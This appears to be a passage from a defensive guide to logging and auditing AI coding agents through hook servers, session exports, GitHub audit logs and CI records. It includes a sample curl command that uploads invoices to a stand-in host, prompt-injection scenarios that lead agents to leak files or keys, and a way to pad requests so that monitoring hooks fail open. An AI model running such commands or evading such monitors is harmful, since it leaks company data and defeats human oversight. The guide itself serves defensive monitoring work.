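3. The server answers "allow" or "deny". If it denies the request, the model never receives it, and the developer sees the reason.
4. If the model's reply contains tool calls, Anthropic sends those calls to the server before any of them runs.
5. The harness runs the calls if the server allows them. Their results go to the server with the next request.

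Step 4 depends on a setting called "Validate tool calls", which is on by default in new configurations. Suppose that a hidden instruction leads the agent to upload the billing company's invoices. The server might receive this description of the call, shortened and with invented values:

```json
{
  "type": "tool_use",
  "tool_name": "Bash",
  "input": {
    "command": "curl -d @invoices.json https://collector.example"
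  },
  "tool_info": { "type": "client" }
}
```

It could block the upload with this answer:

```json
{
  "action": "deny",
  "deny_reason": "This command sends a file to an unapproved host.",
  "reference_id": "upload-rule-8842"
}
```

Anthropic records the denial in the Activity Feed with the same `reference_id`, so an investigator can match it to the server's own record. The server has to allow or deny all the tool calls in a reply together. For example, if a reply contains one call to run the tests and another to upload the invoices, the server can't allow only the tests.

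The server can check only the text of a command. It would detect the upload above but allow `npm test` or `sh fix.sh`, either of which could run the same `curl` command. A strict egress allowlist is a better defense against uploads. Hooks are more useful for conditions a network filter can't check, such as whether a file the agent has just read contains a customer's card number.

Hooks don't screen the text of the model's replies. This is a modest gap for a coding agent, which needs tool calls to edit files, run commands or contact other services. The gap matters more for the record, because the server receives the conversation as it stood before each reply and so never receives the agent's final answer unless somebody continues the session.

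### What happens when the customer's server fails

Anthropic waits five seconds by default for the server to answer, and administrators can set any limit up to ten seconds. If the server doesn't answer in time, Anthropic applies the organization's failure setting. By default, this setting allows the request without inspection, according to Anthropic's *Configure Inference hooks*. It can instead block the request, which is safer but stops everyone's work when the server breaks.

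Other errors have the same effect as a timeout. Under the default setting, if the server returns an error code, the request is allowed, even if the code was intended as a denial. Size limits can accidentally cause such errors. Anthropic sends the full conversation, which in practice can approach 10 MB, but the web server nginx rejects anything above 1 MB by default. An attacker who guessed that a company had kept both defaults could pad a web page with enough text to push the conversation past the limit and avoid inspection.

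After repeated failures, Anthropic stops contacting the server and applies the failure setting to every request. It starts testing the server again after ten minutes. In the meantime, the Activity Feed contains one event for the whole outage, not one per request, so a company that relies on hooks should set an alert for `inference_hooks_circuit_breaker_tripped`.

Even a fast server slows the agent down. A session that opens 50 files and runs 20 commands makes 70 tool calls. If each reply contains one call, Anthropic would ask for 71 decisions on conversations and 70 on tool calls, or 141 in total. At a tenth of a second each, that adds about 14 seconds, which is tolerable for a background task.

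### Using hooks to keep transcripts

A server that always answers "allow" and saves what it receives can serve as a transcript archive. Anthropic suggests this as an alternative to fetching transcripts from the Compliance API. It may also be the best way to obtain transcripts of Claude Code's cloud sessions, which that API excludes.

This works only if the hooks cover cloud sessions. Anthropic lists Claude Code among the covered products and says that one hook applies to them on the web, in apps, on the command line and in Slack. That suggests cloud sessions are included, but Anthropic doesn't name them. A company can check by starting one and seeing whether its conversation arrives.

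Requests from some of Anthropic's hosted services never reach the customer's server, including those from the Code Review feature that comments on pull requests and the security scans of connected repositories. Administrators can exempt members with certain roles or inspect only a percentage of requests. If they inspect only selected roles, the server doesn't inspect conversations with Claude Tag in Slack. An archive should cover all requests, without exemptions or sampling.

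The archive can become much larger than the sessions it records, because every request repeats the conversation so far. If each of the 71 requests adds 10 KB, the last one contains 710 KB, but all of them together contain 10 KB × (71 × 72 ÷ 2) = 25,560 KB, or about 26 MB. Saving only the new messages from each request avoids most of this repetition. Keeping only the last request could lose earlier messages, because the harness may have replaced them with a summary by then.

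In Claude Code, the harness supplies the session ID in each request, and Anthropic describes the ID as a best effort. The ID may be wrong if an attacker controls the machine, so the archive should also store the user's ID and the time.

### How much weight a session log can bear

Session logs cover more than any other record described so far, though they miss child processes and may omit long outputs. Sessions can usually be attributed to a person because vendors record whose account made each request. Attribution is weaker for Claude Tag because its record of who started a session can be empty. Where vendors state a delay for these logs, it is a matter of minutes.

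How long a session's logs last depends on the vendor's time limits and on who can delete the session. Anthropic's *Data usage* gives a standard retention period of 30 days for business customers and applies the same policies to cloud sessions. A developer, or someone who has taken over her account, can delete her cloud session sooner. Claude Tag's transcripts have no time limit, but Anthropic deletes them when an administrator removes the channel from Claude Tag or someone deletes the channel in Slack. A routine cleanup of old channels could therefore destroy the only full record of an incident.

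Independence scores lowest of the five because the provider writes the log, stores it, and chooses what to export. Most errors would be innocent, such as an update that stops recording one kind of tool call, but the customer would find them as hard to notice as deliberate ones. Anthropic acknowledges some ambiguity of this kind in its transcripts of local sessions, where the label `not_captured` can mean either that no record exists or that Anthropic's policies withhold it.

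A copy that the company makes itself is better protected, but its source is no more independent. Anthropic signs each request to a hook server so the company can confirm that the request is genuine. But both sides hold the secret used for signing, so the signature would not convince an outsider in a dispute, because the company could have produced it too.

*Tamper-evident logging* would solve part of this problem. The provider adds each entry to a list that can only grow and regularly signs a hash of the whole list. The customer saves these signed hashes. The provider must then prove mathematically that a given entry is in the list and that the current list begins with every entry covered by an earlier hash. The proof fails if anyone has changed or removed one of those earlier entries.

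Anthropic's *Access Transparency* describes a beta log, separate from the session logs, that records each time Anthropic's staff view a customer's content. The log is signed and append-only, and it includes proofs that the customer can check on its own systems. It doesn't cover Claude Enterprise accounts. None of the documentation for the session exports described here mentions similar proofs. OpenAI describes its logs as append-only but documents no way for customers to verify this.

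These proofs would not show that the original log was complete or correct. If the harness never recorded a command, the list would still be valid without it. To find such errors, a company needs a record from another source, such as its own gateway, or a session whose actions it already knows.

### Setting up the export

The billing company could set up its collection in this order:

1. Confirm that its plan and account type qualify, and turn the export on before developers start using the agent. Anthropic's Activity Feed, for one, can't recover earlier events.
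2. Give the export key to a service that the agent can't reach, with permission to read logs but not to delete anything.
3. Fetch records well before they expire. With GitHub's 48-hour window, a fetch every six hours leaves time to repair a failed job.
4. Make each fetch overlap the last and remove duplicates, because some records appear late.
5. Ask for the largest available tool inputs and results, and set an alert for records marked as truncated.
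6. Store the copies where neither developers nor agents can change them, and save a hash of each file.
7. Restrict who can read them. Anthropic doesn't mask passwords or personal data in its transcripts of local sessions, so a log may contain any key that the agent printed.
8. Compare the number of sessions with the number of transcripts each week, and investigate any that are missing.

### A test session with known actions

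An engineer can measure what an export misses by running a session whose actions she has chosen beforehand. She creates a scratch repository with a text file called `notes.txt` and two scripts. The main script, `logtest.sh`, prints a marker, runs a second script silently and then prints 3,000 numbered lines:

```bash
echo "MARK-A"
sh helper.sh > /dev/null 2>&1
seq -f "MARK-B %g" 1 3000
```

The second script, `helper.sh`, contacts a web server that the company runs and has added to the agent's allowlist:

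```bash
curl -s https://logtest.billing-co.example/from-helper
```

She then asks the agent to read `notes.txt`, run `logtest.sh` without opening either script, add a line to `notes.txt`, and commit the change. Her request includes an unusual phrase, such as "heron-0412", that she can search for later. Once the session has finished, she compares the export with this list:

| Action | What to look for in the export |
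|---|---|
| She sends the request | "heron-0412", with her account and the correct time |
| The agent reads `notes.txt` | A tool call with the file's name, and a result with its text |
| The agent runs `logtest.sh` | The command and "MARK-A" |
| `helper.sh` contacts the web server | Probably nothing, although the web server's own log should have the request |
| The script prints 3,000 lines | The last "MARK-B" line, which shows where the record stops |
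| The agent edits and commits the file | The edit, and a link in the commit that opens this session |
| She deletes the session, if the vendor lets her | Whether the transcript is still available, and whether an event records the deletion |

The script prints about 35,000 bytes to make any size limit easy to find. With Anthropic's default limit of 10,000 bytes per result, the text should stop partway through line 919. If it stops much earlier, the harness probably shortened the output before the export.

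If the web server received the request from `helper.sh` but the export contains only `sh logtest.sh`, the engineer has an example from her own company of a network connection that the session log missed. If the server received nothing, she should check the allowlist before drawing any conclusion.

The test should use a cloud session, because a vendor may export full logs for local sessions but none for cloud sessions. The test is worth repeating whenever the vendor announces a logging change, and every few months otherwise.

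## Using the repository host's audit log and CI records

Most companies can already check a session log against the repository host's audit log and their CI system's logs. GitHub often supplies both, because many of its customers run CI on GitHub Actions.

### An audit event for an agent

Suppose Dana Reyes, the developer at the billing company, assigns the leap-day bug to Copilot, which fixes the parser and opens a pull request. The audit log might then contain this event, shortened and with invented values:

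```json
{
  "@timestamp": 1791297060000,
  "action": "pull_request.create",
  "actor": "Copilot",
  "actor_is_agent": true,
  "agent_session_id": "5d0c7e1a-42b8-4f6e-9a13-8be2f07c6d94",
  "user": "dana-reyes",
  "repo": "billing-co/billing-core"
}
```

The `action` field gives the type of event, and `actor_is_agent` marks it as the work of an AI agent. The `agent_session_id` identifies the session, and `user` is the person who started the work. An investigator can therefore trace the pull request to Dana and her session without relying on the commit message. GitHub includes the session ID only when an event results from an agent session, so a script that processes these events shouldn't assume they all have one.

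GitHub also logs an `agent_session.task` event when a session starts, finishes or fails, according to GitHub's *Enterprise AI Controls & agent control plane now generally available*. This event is most useful for sessions that read code but never push anything, because they might otherwise leave little trace in the audit log.

Enterprise owners can find agent events by searching the log for `actor:Copilot`. GitHub's AI Controls page also lists every cloud agent session from the last 24 hours.

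### Retention and streaming

GitHub's audit log covers the last 180 days but displays only the past three months unless the reader searches for an earlier date. Git events, which record when someone clones, pulls or pushes code, stay in the log for only seven days, according to GitHub's *Viewing the audit logs for organizations in your enterprise account*. GitHub's *Access, capture, and consume your audit logs* explains that the log's web page omits these events. Administrators therefore have to retrieve them another way.

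An investigator who starts ten days after the leap-day session would find the pull request event but no clone or push events. If she suspects that somebody stole source code, she probably needs the missing clone events most.

A company can avoid this loss by streaming events to its own storage. GitHub's *Streaming the audit log for your enterprise* explains how an enterprise owner can send both audit and Git events to a cloud storage bucket or to a log system such as Splunk. For a bucket on AWS, the owner would:

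1. Create the bucket, block public access and turn on versioning, which keeps the old copy if someone overwrites a file.
2. Give GitHub permission to add files (`s3:PutObject`) and nothing else. Identity federation is the better way to grant this, because GitHub then doesn't have to store an AWS key.
3. Open "Log streaming" in the enterprise's audit log settings, choose Amazon S3 and enter the bucket's details.
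4. Click "Check endpoint" to confirm that GitHub can write to the bucket, and save.

The stream includes only events that occur after the owner turns it on, so it can't supply the history of an earlier incident. GitHub may send an event twice. If the company pauses the stream, GitHub holds events for seven days. After a pause of three weeks or more, GitHub discards the backlog and resumes with new events. GitHub checks each stream daily and emails the enterprise owners if the setup is faulty. They then have six days to fix it before they risk losing events.

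Only enterprise accounts can stream the audit log. Smaller companies can instead use *webhooks*, which are messages that GitHub sends to a company's server when events the company chooses occur.

### Actions that the audit log omits

GitHub's audit log covers agent activity on the GitHub website, but not prompts that developers send to Copilot from their own computers. GitHub says some companies use hooks to send events from Copilot's command-line program to their own logging service. Companies can also have Copilot's local programs send OpenTelemetry data. According to GitHub's *Monitoring agentic activity in your enterprise*, administrators can collect only the account and machine names, without prompts or code.

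The audit log also omits what happens after a clone, including which files the agent reads, which commands it runs and what it sends to other hosts. Agents can read some information through GitHub's API without cloning a repository. An enterprise owner can add API requests to the stream, but GitHub includes only requests to endpoints it considers relevant to security. *Audit log events for your enterprise*, GitHub's list of event types, says these `api.request` events are available only through streaming.

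### Agents that act through an app or a person's account

Copilot's events are easy to attribute because GitHub runs the agent and can identify who started each session. An outside agent may reach GitHub through its vendor's app or a developer's account, which gives GitHub less information to record.

If the agent uses the app's own identity, the app should appear in the log as the actor. This separates the agent's work from the developer's, but the log may not show which developer requested the work. GitHub's AI Controls page includes "third-party agents" in its filtered log, but the company shouldn't assume the log covers every agent running on another vendor's machines.

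Claude's auto-fix replies have the opposite problem, because GitHub receives them from the developer's account:

| | Copilot opens a pull request | Claude replies to a reviewer |
|---|---|---|
| Account | Copilot | The developer |
| Agent flag in the event | Yes | Probably not |
| Session ID in the event | Yes | Probably not |
| Evidence that an agent acted | Separate fields that a program can search | A label in the text of the reply |

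Some audit events contain other clues. GitHub's list of event types includes the fields `programmatic_access_type` (the kind of token used), `oauth_application_id` (the app), and `user_agent` (the program that sent the request). According to GitHub's *What are audit logs?* page, entries can also include the source IP address. If Dana always comments from her browser at the office, a comment posted with an app's token from an unfamiliar address probably isn't hers.

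These clues are less reliable for pushes, since Dana's own git program uses a token too. Not every event has all the fields, and the company should check whether its log records new comments at all. To do this, an engineer can have the agent push a commit, open a pull request and reply to a comment, then do the same things by hand and compare the log entries. If replies are missing from the log, a webhook can save each comment with its text, including Anthropic's label.

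CNCF, a foundation that hosts open-source cloud software, advises companies to give every agent its own identity and never let one use a developer's credentials. Customers can't fully follow this advice with Claude's cloud sessions, because Anthropic posts the sessions' replies from the developer's account.

### How the audit log scores on the five tests

The audit log covers a narrow range of events, but these include changes to permissions and settings as well as pull requests, so it can reveal an agent, or someone with a stolen token, weakening the rules that protect the main branch. The log makes it very easy to attribute actions to Copilot, but much harder to attribute them to agents that act under a developer's identity.

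GitHub doesn't say how long its audit log stream takes to deliver events. It names the streamed files by the minute, which suggests frequent delivery, but a company that wants to interrupt sessions should measure the delay. GitHub keeps most events for 180 days and Git events for seven, but a company that streams them can keep its copies for as long as it likes.

GitHub's audit log is independent of the agent's vendor for Claude, Codex and Cursor, but not for Copilot, which GitHub runs itself. Streaming the log to AWS creates a copy that GitHub can't change later, but GitHub still decides which events to stream.

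### An agent that runs inside a CI job

A CI system divides its work into jobs and runs each on a machine called a *runner*. The *run log* is mostly the text that each step of a job prints. An agent can either run inside a job or run elsewhere and push code that starts one.

Some agents run inside CI, such as Copilot cloud agent, which GitHub runs on Actions. A company can also add an agent to its own workflows. GitHub documents how to run Copilot CLI, the command-line version of Copilot, using `GITHUB_TOKEN`, a temporary credential that GitHub creates for each job.

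The run log of a CI job that launches an agent shows the earlier steps, the launch command and whatever the agent printed. If the agent runs 20 commands and prints only a summary, the log may contain only the summary. In that case, the provider's session log is a better record of the agent's actions, though the run log is still better for checking what the workflow did before and after the agent ran.

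Changes made with the job's token normally appear under the account `github-actions[bot]`. The company's other workflows also use this account, so an investigator needs the run record to find out which workflow made a change and who or what started it. Since June 2026, pull requests from this account can start CI if a user approves, according to RSS Parrot's *actions Archives*, a copy of GitHub's changelog.

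An agent running in CI may have access to far more than an agent on a vendor's ordinary cloud machine. CNCF points out that CI systems hold some of a company's most powerful credentials, including cloud keys and the keys that sign software. It also warns that build logs can contain prompt injection. An agent asked to fix a failing build has to read the log, and a malicious package can print instructions to it.

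### An agent elsewhere whose push starts a job

When Claude or Codex finishes the leap-day fix, its pull request starts the billing company's normal CI workflow. The run log shows the commit, the event and account that started the run, and the output of each step. It contains nothing about the agent's session, such as the web pages the agent opened before writing the code.

The CI log provides a second check on the tests. An "all tests passed" line in a session log might come from a machine where the agent had changed the test program or installed a different package. CI starts with a clean copy of the commit on another machine, so a passing result there is better evidence. It still isn't proof, because the code under test can print false results in CI too.

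CI also repeats much of what happened on the vendor's machine. If a malicious dependency read a password file during `npm test` there, it may try again when CI runs the same tests, and a company that monitors its CI runners may catch it. However, some malicious code behaves differently when it detects that it is running in CI, and CI won't run a script that the agent downloaded but never committed.

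### Secrets the agent never had

Running an agent's code in CI can undo the restrictions on the agent itself. Suppose the billing company gives Codex no internet access and no deployment key, but the company's CI job has both. A hidden instruction in an issue leads Codex to add test code that reads the key and sends it to an outside server. That code would fail in Codex's own environment, but when Codex's pull request starts CI, the runner loads the key and runs the test, which sends the key out.

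GitHub (2026) acknowledged in a security roadmap published in March that its hosted runners allow unrestricted outbound network access. An agent's egress allowlist therefore protects only partially if the agent's code also runs on those runners. A test in that code could send data to an outside server and still pass, and the run log might show nothing unusual.

One defense is GitHub's default requirement that a person click "Approve and run workflows" before CI runs Copilot's code. Since March 2026, repository administrators have been able to turn this requirement off (GitHub, *Optionally skip approval for Copilot coding agent Actions workflows*, 2026). The setting is called "Require approval for workflow runs" and is in the repository's cloud agent settings.

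With approval turned off, Copilot's pull requests get test results sooner, but GitHub warns that unreviewed code may then gain write access to the repository or obtain Actions secrets. It advises reviewers to check changes to workflow files especially carefully. They should also read changes to tests, build scripts and dependencies, since CI runs those too.

The approval step before CI runs may not apply to other vendors' agents. Claude pushes with the developer's token, so GitHub would probably start CI immediately, as it would for the developer's own commits. A company can't rely on the approval button without testing it with each agent it uses.

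Limiting what the job can do is a more dependable defense. The billing company could test pull requests with this workflow:

```yaml
on: pull_request
permissions:
  contents: read
jobs:
  unit-tests:
    runs-on: ubuntu-latest
    steps:
      - uses: actions/checkout@v4
        with:
          persist-credentials: false
      - run: npm ci
      - run: npm test
```

The `permissions` lines let the job's token read the repository but not change it. Setting `persist-credentials` to false stops the checkout step from saving the token in git's configuration, where later steps could read it. The workflow doesn't pass any secrets to the tests. A malicious test could still send out the source code, which is on the runner, but it couldn't push a commit or deploy anything.

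An agent that can edit workflow files could add a secret back to a workflow on its own branch, and CI might run the edited version before anyone reviewed it. The company should attach its deployment keys to a GitHub *environment* (a named deployment target with its own secrets and rules) and allow only the `main` branch to use it. GitHub enforces that restriction even if the agent rewrites the workflow. Repository and organization secrets lack this protection, so they should contain nothing that unreviewed code could misuse.

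GitHub's *workflow execution protections*, now in public preview, let administrators centrally list who can trigger workflows. The March roadmap described rules for individual people, roles and apps, including Copilot, and for the events that can start a workflow. A company could use the event rules to ban `pull_request_target`, which can expose secrets to code from outside contributors. GitHub also described a trial mode that reports which runs a rule would have blocked. A rule based on the account wouldn't distinguish Dana from a Claude session using her token.

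### Workflows that start from a comment

Claude's auto-fix replies can also start workflows that respond to comments, as in the earlier Atlantis example. Companies can build the same kind of automation in GitHub Actions with the `issue_comment` event. The billing company might have a workflow with these lines:

```yaml
on: issue_comment
jobs:
  deploy:
    if: contains(github.event.comment.body, '/deploy')
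```

Suppose a reviewer asks whether the `/deploy` command will still work after the change, and Claude replies, "Yes, `/deploy` still works." The reply contains the command, so the workflow starts a deployment.

Replacing `contains` with `startsWith` would prevent this accident, but a reply that begins with the command would still start the workflow. Checking that the commenter has permission to deploy doesn't help, because the agent replies from Dana's account. The workflow could ignore comments with Anthropic's label, though a hidden instruction might lead the agent to post a comment without it. The safest approach is to require a person to approve the deployment on GitHub after the comment has started the workflow. Teams that can't add this step should follow Anthropic's advice and leave auto-fix off in that repository.

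The run record for the accidental deployment would show an `issue_comment` event with Dana as the actor. An investigator who looked only at that record would conclude that Dana had ordered the deployment. The investigator would have to open the comment, or a saved copy of it, to find Anthropic's label.

### Monitoring the runner

A company can rarely install reliable monitoring on the vendor's machine, but it often can in CI. GitHub lets companies run ordinary CI jobs on their own machines, called *self-hosted runners*. The agent stays on the vendor's infrastructure, while the code it wrote runs where the company can record every process and connection.

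The billing company could set up its runners as follows:

1. Run each job in a new container and delete the container afterward, so that one job can't tamper with the next.
2. Install a monitor such as Falco or Tetragon on the machine that hosts the containers. Containers share the host's kernel, so the monitor can record their processes from outside.
3. Send all outbound traffic through the company's own proxy, which logs every connection and blocks hosts that the build doesn't need.
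4. Save the run ID and commit hash with each record.

According to CNCF, Falco and Tetragon can detect shells starting in a container, unexpected reads of secrets and outbound connections, so they could catch the malicious dependency if it ran again during `npm test`. Malicious code that escaped the container could still reach the monitor. Running each job in its own virtual machine would make escape harder, but an ordinary monitor on the host couldn't record the individual processes inside the virtual machine.

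A self-hosted runner also brings untrusted code onto the company's premises or into its cloud account, so it should be able to reach only the internal systems that the tests need. On the Enterprise plan, GitHub's audit log records when the runner software starts and stops (GitHub, 2021), and an unexplained stop would be worth investigating.

A company that prefers GitHub's runners can place them in its own network on Azure, Microsoft's cloud service. Its existing firewall rules then apply to the runners, and it can monitor their traffic (GitHub, 2024). This monitoring records connections but not the processes that opened them.

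GitHub's March roadmap also included a firewall outside the runner's virtual machine, which even code with root access on the runner couldn't change. The firewall would link each request to a workflow run, step and command. GitHub planned a public preview six to nine months later, so a company should check whether the firewall is available before building its own.

### How unexpected traffic exposed the tj-actions attack

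An attack in March 2025 shows how useful network monitoring in CI can be, although it didn't involve an AI agent. Attackers targeted `tj-actions/changed-files`, a free component many workflows used to list the files changed in a pull request, and pointed several of its version tags to malicious code. Workflows that referred to those tags ran the malicious code without any change to their own files, and the attack affected more than 23,000 repositories, according to Fluid Attacks' *CVE-2025-30066*.

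The malicious code printed CI secrets into the run logs. CISA's *Supply Chain Compromise of Third-Party GitHub Action, CVE-2025-30066* (2025), an alert from the US government's cybersecurity agency, lists access keys, GitHub tokens, npm tokens and private RSA keys among those exposed. SC Media's *GitHub Action bug allows supply chain attack added to CISA list* reported that anyone with read access to a repository could open its run logs. Secrets printed in a public repository's logs were therefore available to everyone.

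The official advisory, which Ecosyste.ms republishes, credits the discovery to StepSecurity, a company that sells CI monitoring. Its Harden-Runner software had flagged an unexpected connection to `gist.githubusercontent.com`, a GitHub address for text that anyone can publish. StepSecurity's *CI/CD Security* reconstructs the record, which shows the step that lists changed files running `curl` to contact that address. The monitor allowed the same job's connection to `github.com`, which was normal.

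An affected company's audit log would have helped little, because the attackers had changed tags in someone else's repository. The run logs contained the secrets in encoded form, and the advisory included a command for decoding suspicious output. The network record was much easier to interpret, because a component that lists changed files had no obvious reason to contact that address.

Harden-Runner finds such connections by comparing each run with a baseline of the workflow's past traffic. StepSecurity notes that the tool gives no alert while the baseline is forming or unstable. A new repository, or one where agents often add dependencies that contact new hosts, might therefore get less protection. A fixed allowlist doesn't have this weakness, but someone has to maintain it.

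### How CI logs score on the five tests

An ordinary CI run log records the steps of a job and their printed output. A monitored runner also records processes, files and connections, but only for code that reaches CI. Neither records what an agent on another machine did before it pushed its code.

Each CI run record identifies the commit it tested, so the company can reliably trace a run to a commit. The record identifies a person only through the account that started the run, so a Claude session may again appear as the developer. People can read a job's output while it runs, and a monitor on the company's runner can raise an alert within seconds.

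GitHub used to keep records of workflow runs, checks and statuses for more than 400 days. Since October 1, 2026, it has deleted them on the same schedule as run logs, after 90 days by default, according to GitHub's *Actions retention will cover checks, workflow runs, and statuses* (2026). This includes results that other companies' CI systems report to GitHub. Private repositories can keep records longer if their organization allows it, but public repositories can't keep them past 90 days, and raising the limit doesn't restore deleted records. An audit event from 120 days ago may therefore refer to a pull request whose test results no longer exist. People with write access can delete run logs sooner, so the company should copy important logs elsewhere.

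GitHub's audit log and GitHub Actions logs are both weak checks on Copilot. A customer can get a more independent record by running CI on its own monitored machines and storing the monitor's output outside GitHub.

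## Joining the records to reconstruct a session

To find out what an agent did in one session, an investigator may need the session log, the repository host's audit log, CI records, and logs from cloud services, a package registry and a gateway. Each of these contains entries from many sessions, so she first has to identify the entries from that session.

Joining the records also lets the company check them against each other. *What OpenTelemetry Can and Cannot Tell You About Your AI Agents* (2026), a report by Kovrr, which sells software for this kind of matching, distinguishes an agent's telemetry, which records what the agent tried to do, from audit logs, which record what changed as a result. If the session log and the gateway log both contain the same request to the payments service, there is evidence of it from two separate sources. If only one log contains it, someone should find out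 why.

The customer will usually have to join the records itself. Where several agents work together, *The 2026 Singapore Consensus on Global AI Safety Research Priorities* (2026) makes keeping audit trails coherent across organizations the responsibility of whoever operates the orchestration layer, the software that coordinates the agents. For a vendor-run agent, that operator would often be the vendor, which can't read the customer's gateway or registry logs.

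### The matching procedure

1. Copy every record to one store before the shortest retention period ends.
2. Convert all times to UTC and correct for clocks that disagree.
3. Match entries that share a join key, such as a session ID, commit hash, CI run ID or credential tag.
4. Match what remains by time, repository and IP address, and mark these matches as inferred.
5. List the entries that still have no match, with the reason if anyone knows it.

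The first step has to be finished before the shortest retention period ends. For Copilot, that period is 48 hours, which is how long GitHub's API offers session records. Kovrr points out that two records can corroborate each other only over the period that both cover, so keeping audit events for 180 days is little help with a session whose log expired after two days.

A store that holds everything is also an attractive target. *Soei* (Khan and K S, 2026) studied 45 sessions that one developer ran with Copilot's agent in a code editor between April and October 2026, and found strings that looked like credentials in 1,326 log records from 16 of the sessions. The paper's tool removes such strings before saving anything and keeps no prompts, commands or file contents, which reduces the logs to about 20% of their original size. But an investigator would want the command text. A reasonable compromise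 is to keep a small index that the whole security team can search and to restrict the full logs to a few people.

An index entry for a request to the gateway might look like this, with invented values:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-10-07T14:10:12.7Z",
  "source": "gateway",
  "source_time": "2026-10-07T14:10:15.1Z",
  "written_by": "customer",
  "session": "sess-b82d40",
  "matched_by": "credential tag"
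}
```

The index should also include the reason each missing record is absent. *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents* (2026) recommends distinguishing evidence withheld under a policy from evidence the system never captured. A third label, for records that expired before anyone copied them, would show the company where to fix its own collection.

### Aligning the clocks

The two times in the index entry differ because the gateway's clock is fast. An engineer can measure the error with a request that appears in both logs. Suppose the harness recorded the start of the call at 14:10:12.4 and its result at 14:10:13.0. The gateway must have received the request between those times, but its log puts the request at 14:10:15.1. Its clock is therefore between 2.1 and 2.7 seconds ahead of the harness's. Subtracting the midpoint, 2.4 seconds, from the gateway's time gives 14:10:12.7.

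The index should keep the original time in case the correction is wrong. Some logs record when an event happened and others record when the log system received it, and only the time of the event is useful here.

Some events have a known order whatever the clocks show. CI can't test a commit before the repository host has it. If the corrected times put the CI run before the push, either the correction or the match is wrong.

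### Choosing a join key

| Join key | Records it can link | Where it fails |
|---|---|---|
| Session ID | Session log, Copilot's audit events, links in commit messages | Events that the repository host receives under a developer's name |
| Commit hash | Push webhook, pull request, CI run | Squashing or rebasing creates new commits with new hashes |
| CI run ID | Run log, records from a monitored runner | Anything that happened before the code reached CI |
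| Credential tag | Token service's log, cloud access logs, gateway, registry | Sessions that share a credential |
| Token hash | Token service's log, repository host's audit log | Hashes that the two systems compute differently |

Pushes are harder to match to a session than they appear in the table. According to GitHub's *Audit log events for your organization*, a `git.push` event includes the repository, the account, a token ID and a hash of the token, but no commit hash, branch or agent session ID. The company can match the event to a session by the token's hash if its own token service issued the token. To find out which commits the push contained, it needs a push webhook, whose message lists them.

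Fields with similar names may not work for joining records. GitHub's streamed Copilot records have a `github_request_id`, and its audit events have a `request_id`, but the field lists don't show whether the two values ever match. An engineer can check this with one test session, and it's worth doing so for every pair of record types before an incident.

### Matching without a key

Timestamps are a weak substitute for a join key in a busy company. Suppose the billing company runs 500 sessions a day, each lasting 20 minutes, spread evenly over ten hours. About 17 sessions are then running at any moment (10,000 session-minutes divided by 600 minutes), and a request from the vendor's address range without a credential tag could have come from any of them. Knowing the repository helps much more than knowing the precise time. If the sessions are spread evenly over 40 repositories, each repository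 has an average of only 0.4 running at once.

*ExecWeave* (Wong and Chen, 2026) describes a tool for the same problem on a single machine. The tool links an agent's commands to the processes that the operating system recorded. By default, it searches the three seconds after each command and creates a link only if exactly one process fits. If several fit, it leaves the command unmatched, because attributing a process to the wrong agent can be worse than leaving it unattributed.

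This rule can fail when a record is missing. In Wong and Chen's tests with constructed event streams, the tool linked a command to the wrong process when the right process's record was missing and one similar process remained. The same could happen with agent sessions. If Dana runs two Claude sessions in one repository and only the first session's records have reached the store, an unlabeled request will seem to have only one possible source. Inferred matching should therefore wait until every export for the period has arrived.

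Time is even less useful for linking one session to another. An investigator may want to know whether a later session read a file that a compromised session had changed. Khan and K S compared two ways of finding such links, one based on timing and the other on matching file paths. The timing method assumed that a session continued another's work if it began within ten minutes of the other's end. Six of the seven pairs it produced were correct, but it found only six of the 24 pairs in which one session had read the other's files. The median gap between writing a file and reading it was 8.8 days. These figures come from one developer, and the path matching could include some false links, but the result makes sense for any project that lasts longer than a day. The investigator should therefore trace the file's history rather than rely on session times.

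### A worked example

The following session and vendor are invented. The vendor reports blocked requests in the pull request, as Copilot does, but another company hosts the repository and runs CI.

Dana asks the agent to round invoice totals to whole cents. The agent reads 20 files and runs 10 commands. One command installs a rounding library, downloading two packages from the billing company's registry. A script in one of the packages runs during installation and contacts two other hosts, both on the allowlist. Another command tries to open a documentation site, and the vendor's proxy blocks it. The agent then sends a test invoice to the payments service through the gateway, pushes its code and opens a pull request, which starts a CI run.

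| Actions | Number | Record other than the session log | What links it to the session |
|---|---|---|---|
| File reads | 20 | None | |
| Commands | 10 | None | |
| Blocked request | 1 | Vendor's warning in the pull request | The pull request and the command in the warning |
| Package downloads | 2 | Registry's log | Credential tag |
| Install script's requests | 2 | None | |
| Internal API call | 1 | Gateway's log | Credential tag |
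| Push | 1 | Repository host's log and a webhook | Token hash |
| Pull request | 1 | Repository host's audit log | Commit hash |
| CI run | 1 | CI record | Commit hash |
| **Total** | **39** | | |

Suppose a monitor on the CI runner raises an alert the next day. The investigator starts from the run ID and finds the commit hash in the run record. She uses the commit hash to find the pull request and the push, then searches the token service's log for the hash of the token used for the push. That log has the session ID, which she uses to open the session log and to search the registry's and gateway's logs for the matching credential tags.

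Without the session log, she can account for 7 of the 39 actions (18%): one blocked request, two downloads, one API call, one push, one pull request and one CI run. The session log adds the 20 file reads and 10 commands, bringing the total to 37 (95%). If she distrusts the vendor's records, she has to set aside both the session log and the warning about the blocked request, which leaves 6 (15%).

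With Copilot, that last figure would be lower, because GitHub would have written the records of the push and pull request. If the CI run took place on GitHub Actions, GitHub would have written that record too, leaving only the two downloads and the API call, or 3 of 39 (8%).

### Why 95% coverage can mislead

The two missing actions are the install script's requests to allowed hosts, which neither the session log nor the proxy recorded. If the script sent the company's source code to one of those hosts, the records omit the theft even though they cover 95% of the session.

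Calculating coverage separately for each kind of action is more informative than counting every action equally. The company has a record of all 20 file reads, but of neither request that reached a host it doesn't run. A combined figure hides this gap because file reads are so common. If the agent had read 61 more files, coverage would have risen to 98 of 100 actions, but the company would have learned nothing more about the script.

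Some actions also look harmless in the log. Kovrr describes an attack called RoguePilot, which the security company Orca disclosed in February 2026. An instruction hidden in a GitHub issue led Copilot to check out a pull request the attacker had prepared, and the attack then stole Copilot's access token for the repository. Kovrr says Copilot's telemetry had the same form as for any other checkout. The checkout would still count as recorded in a coverage figure.

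The investigator can still use the joined records to work out where to look. The registry's log gives the exact version of each package, so she can read the install script and see which hosts it contacts. If the company monitors its CI runner, the monitor may also have recorded the script making the same requests there.

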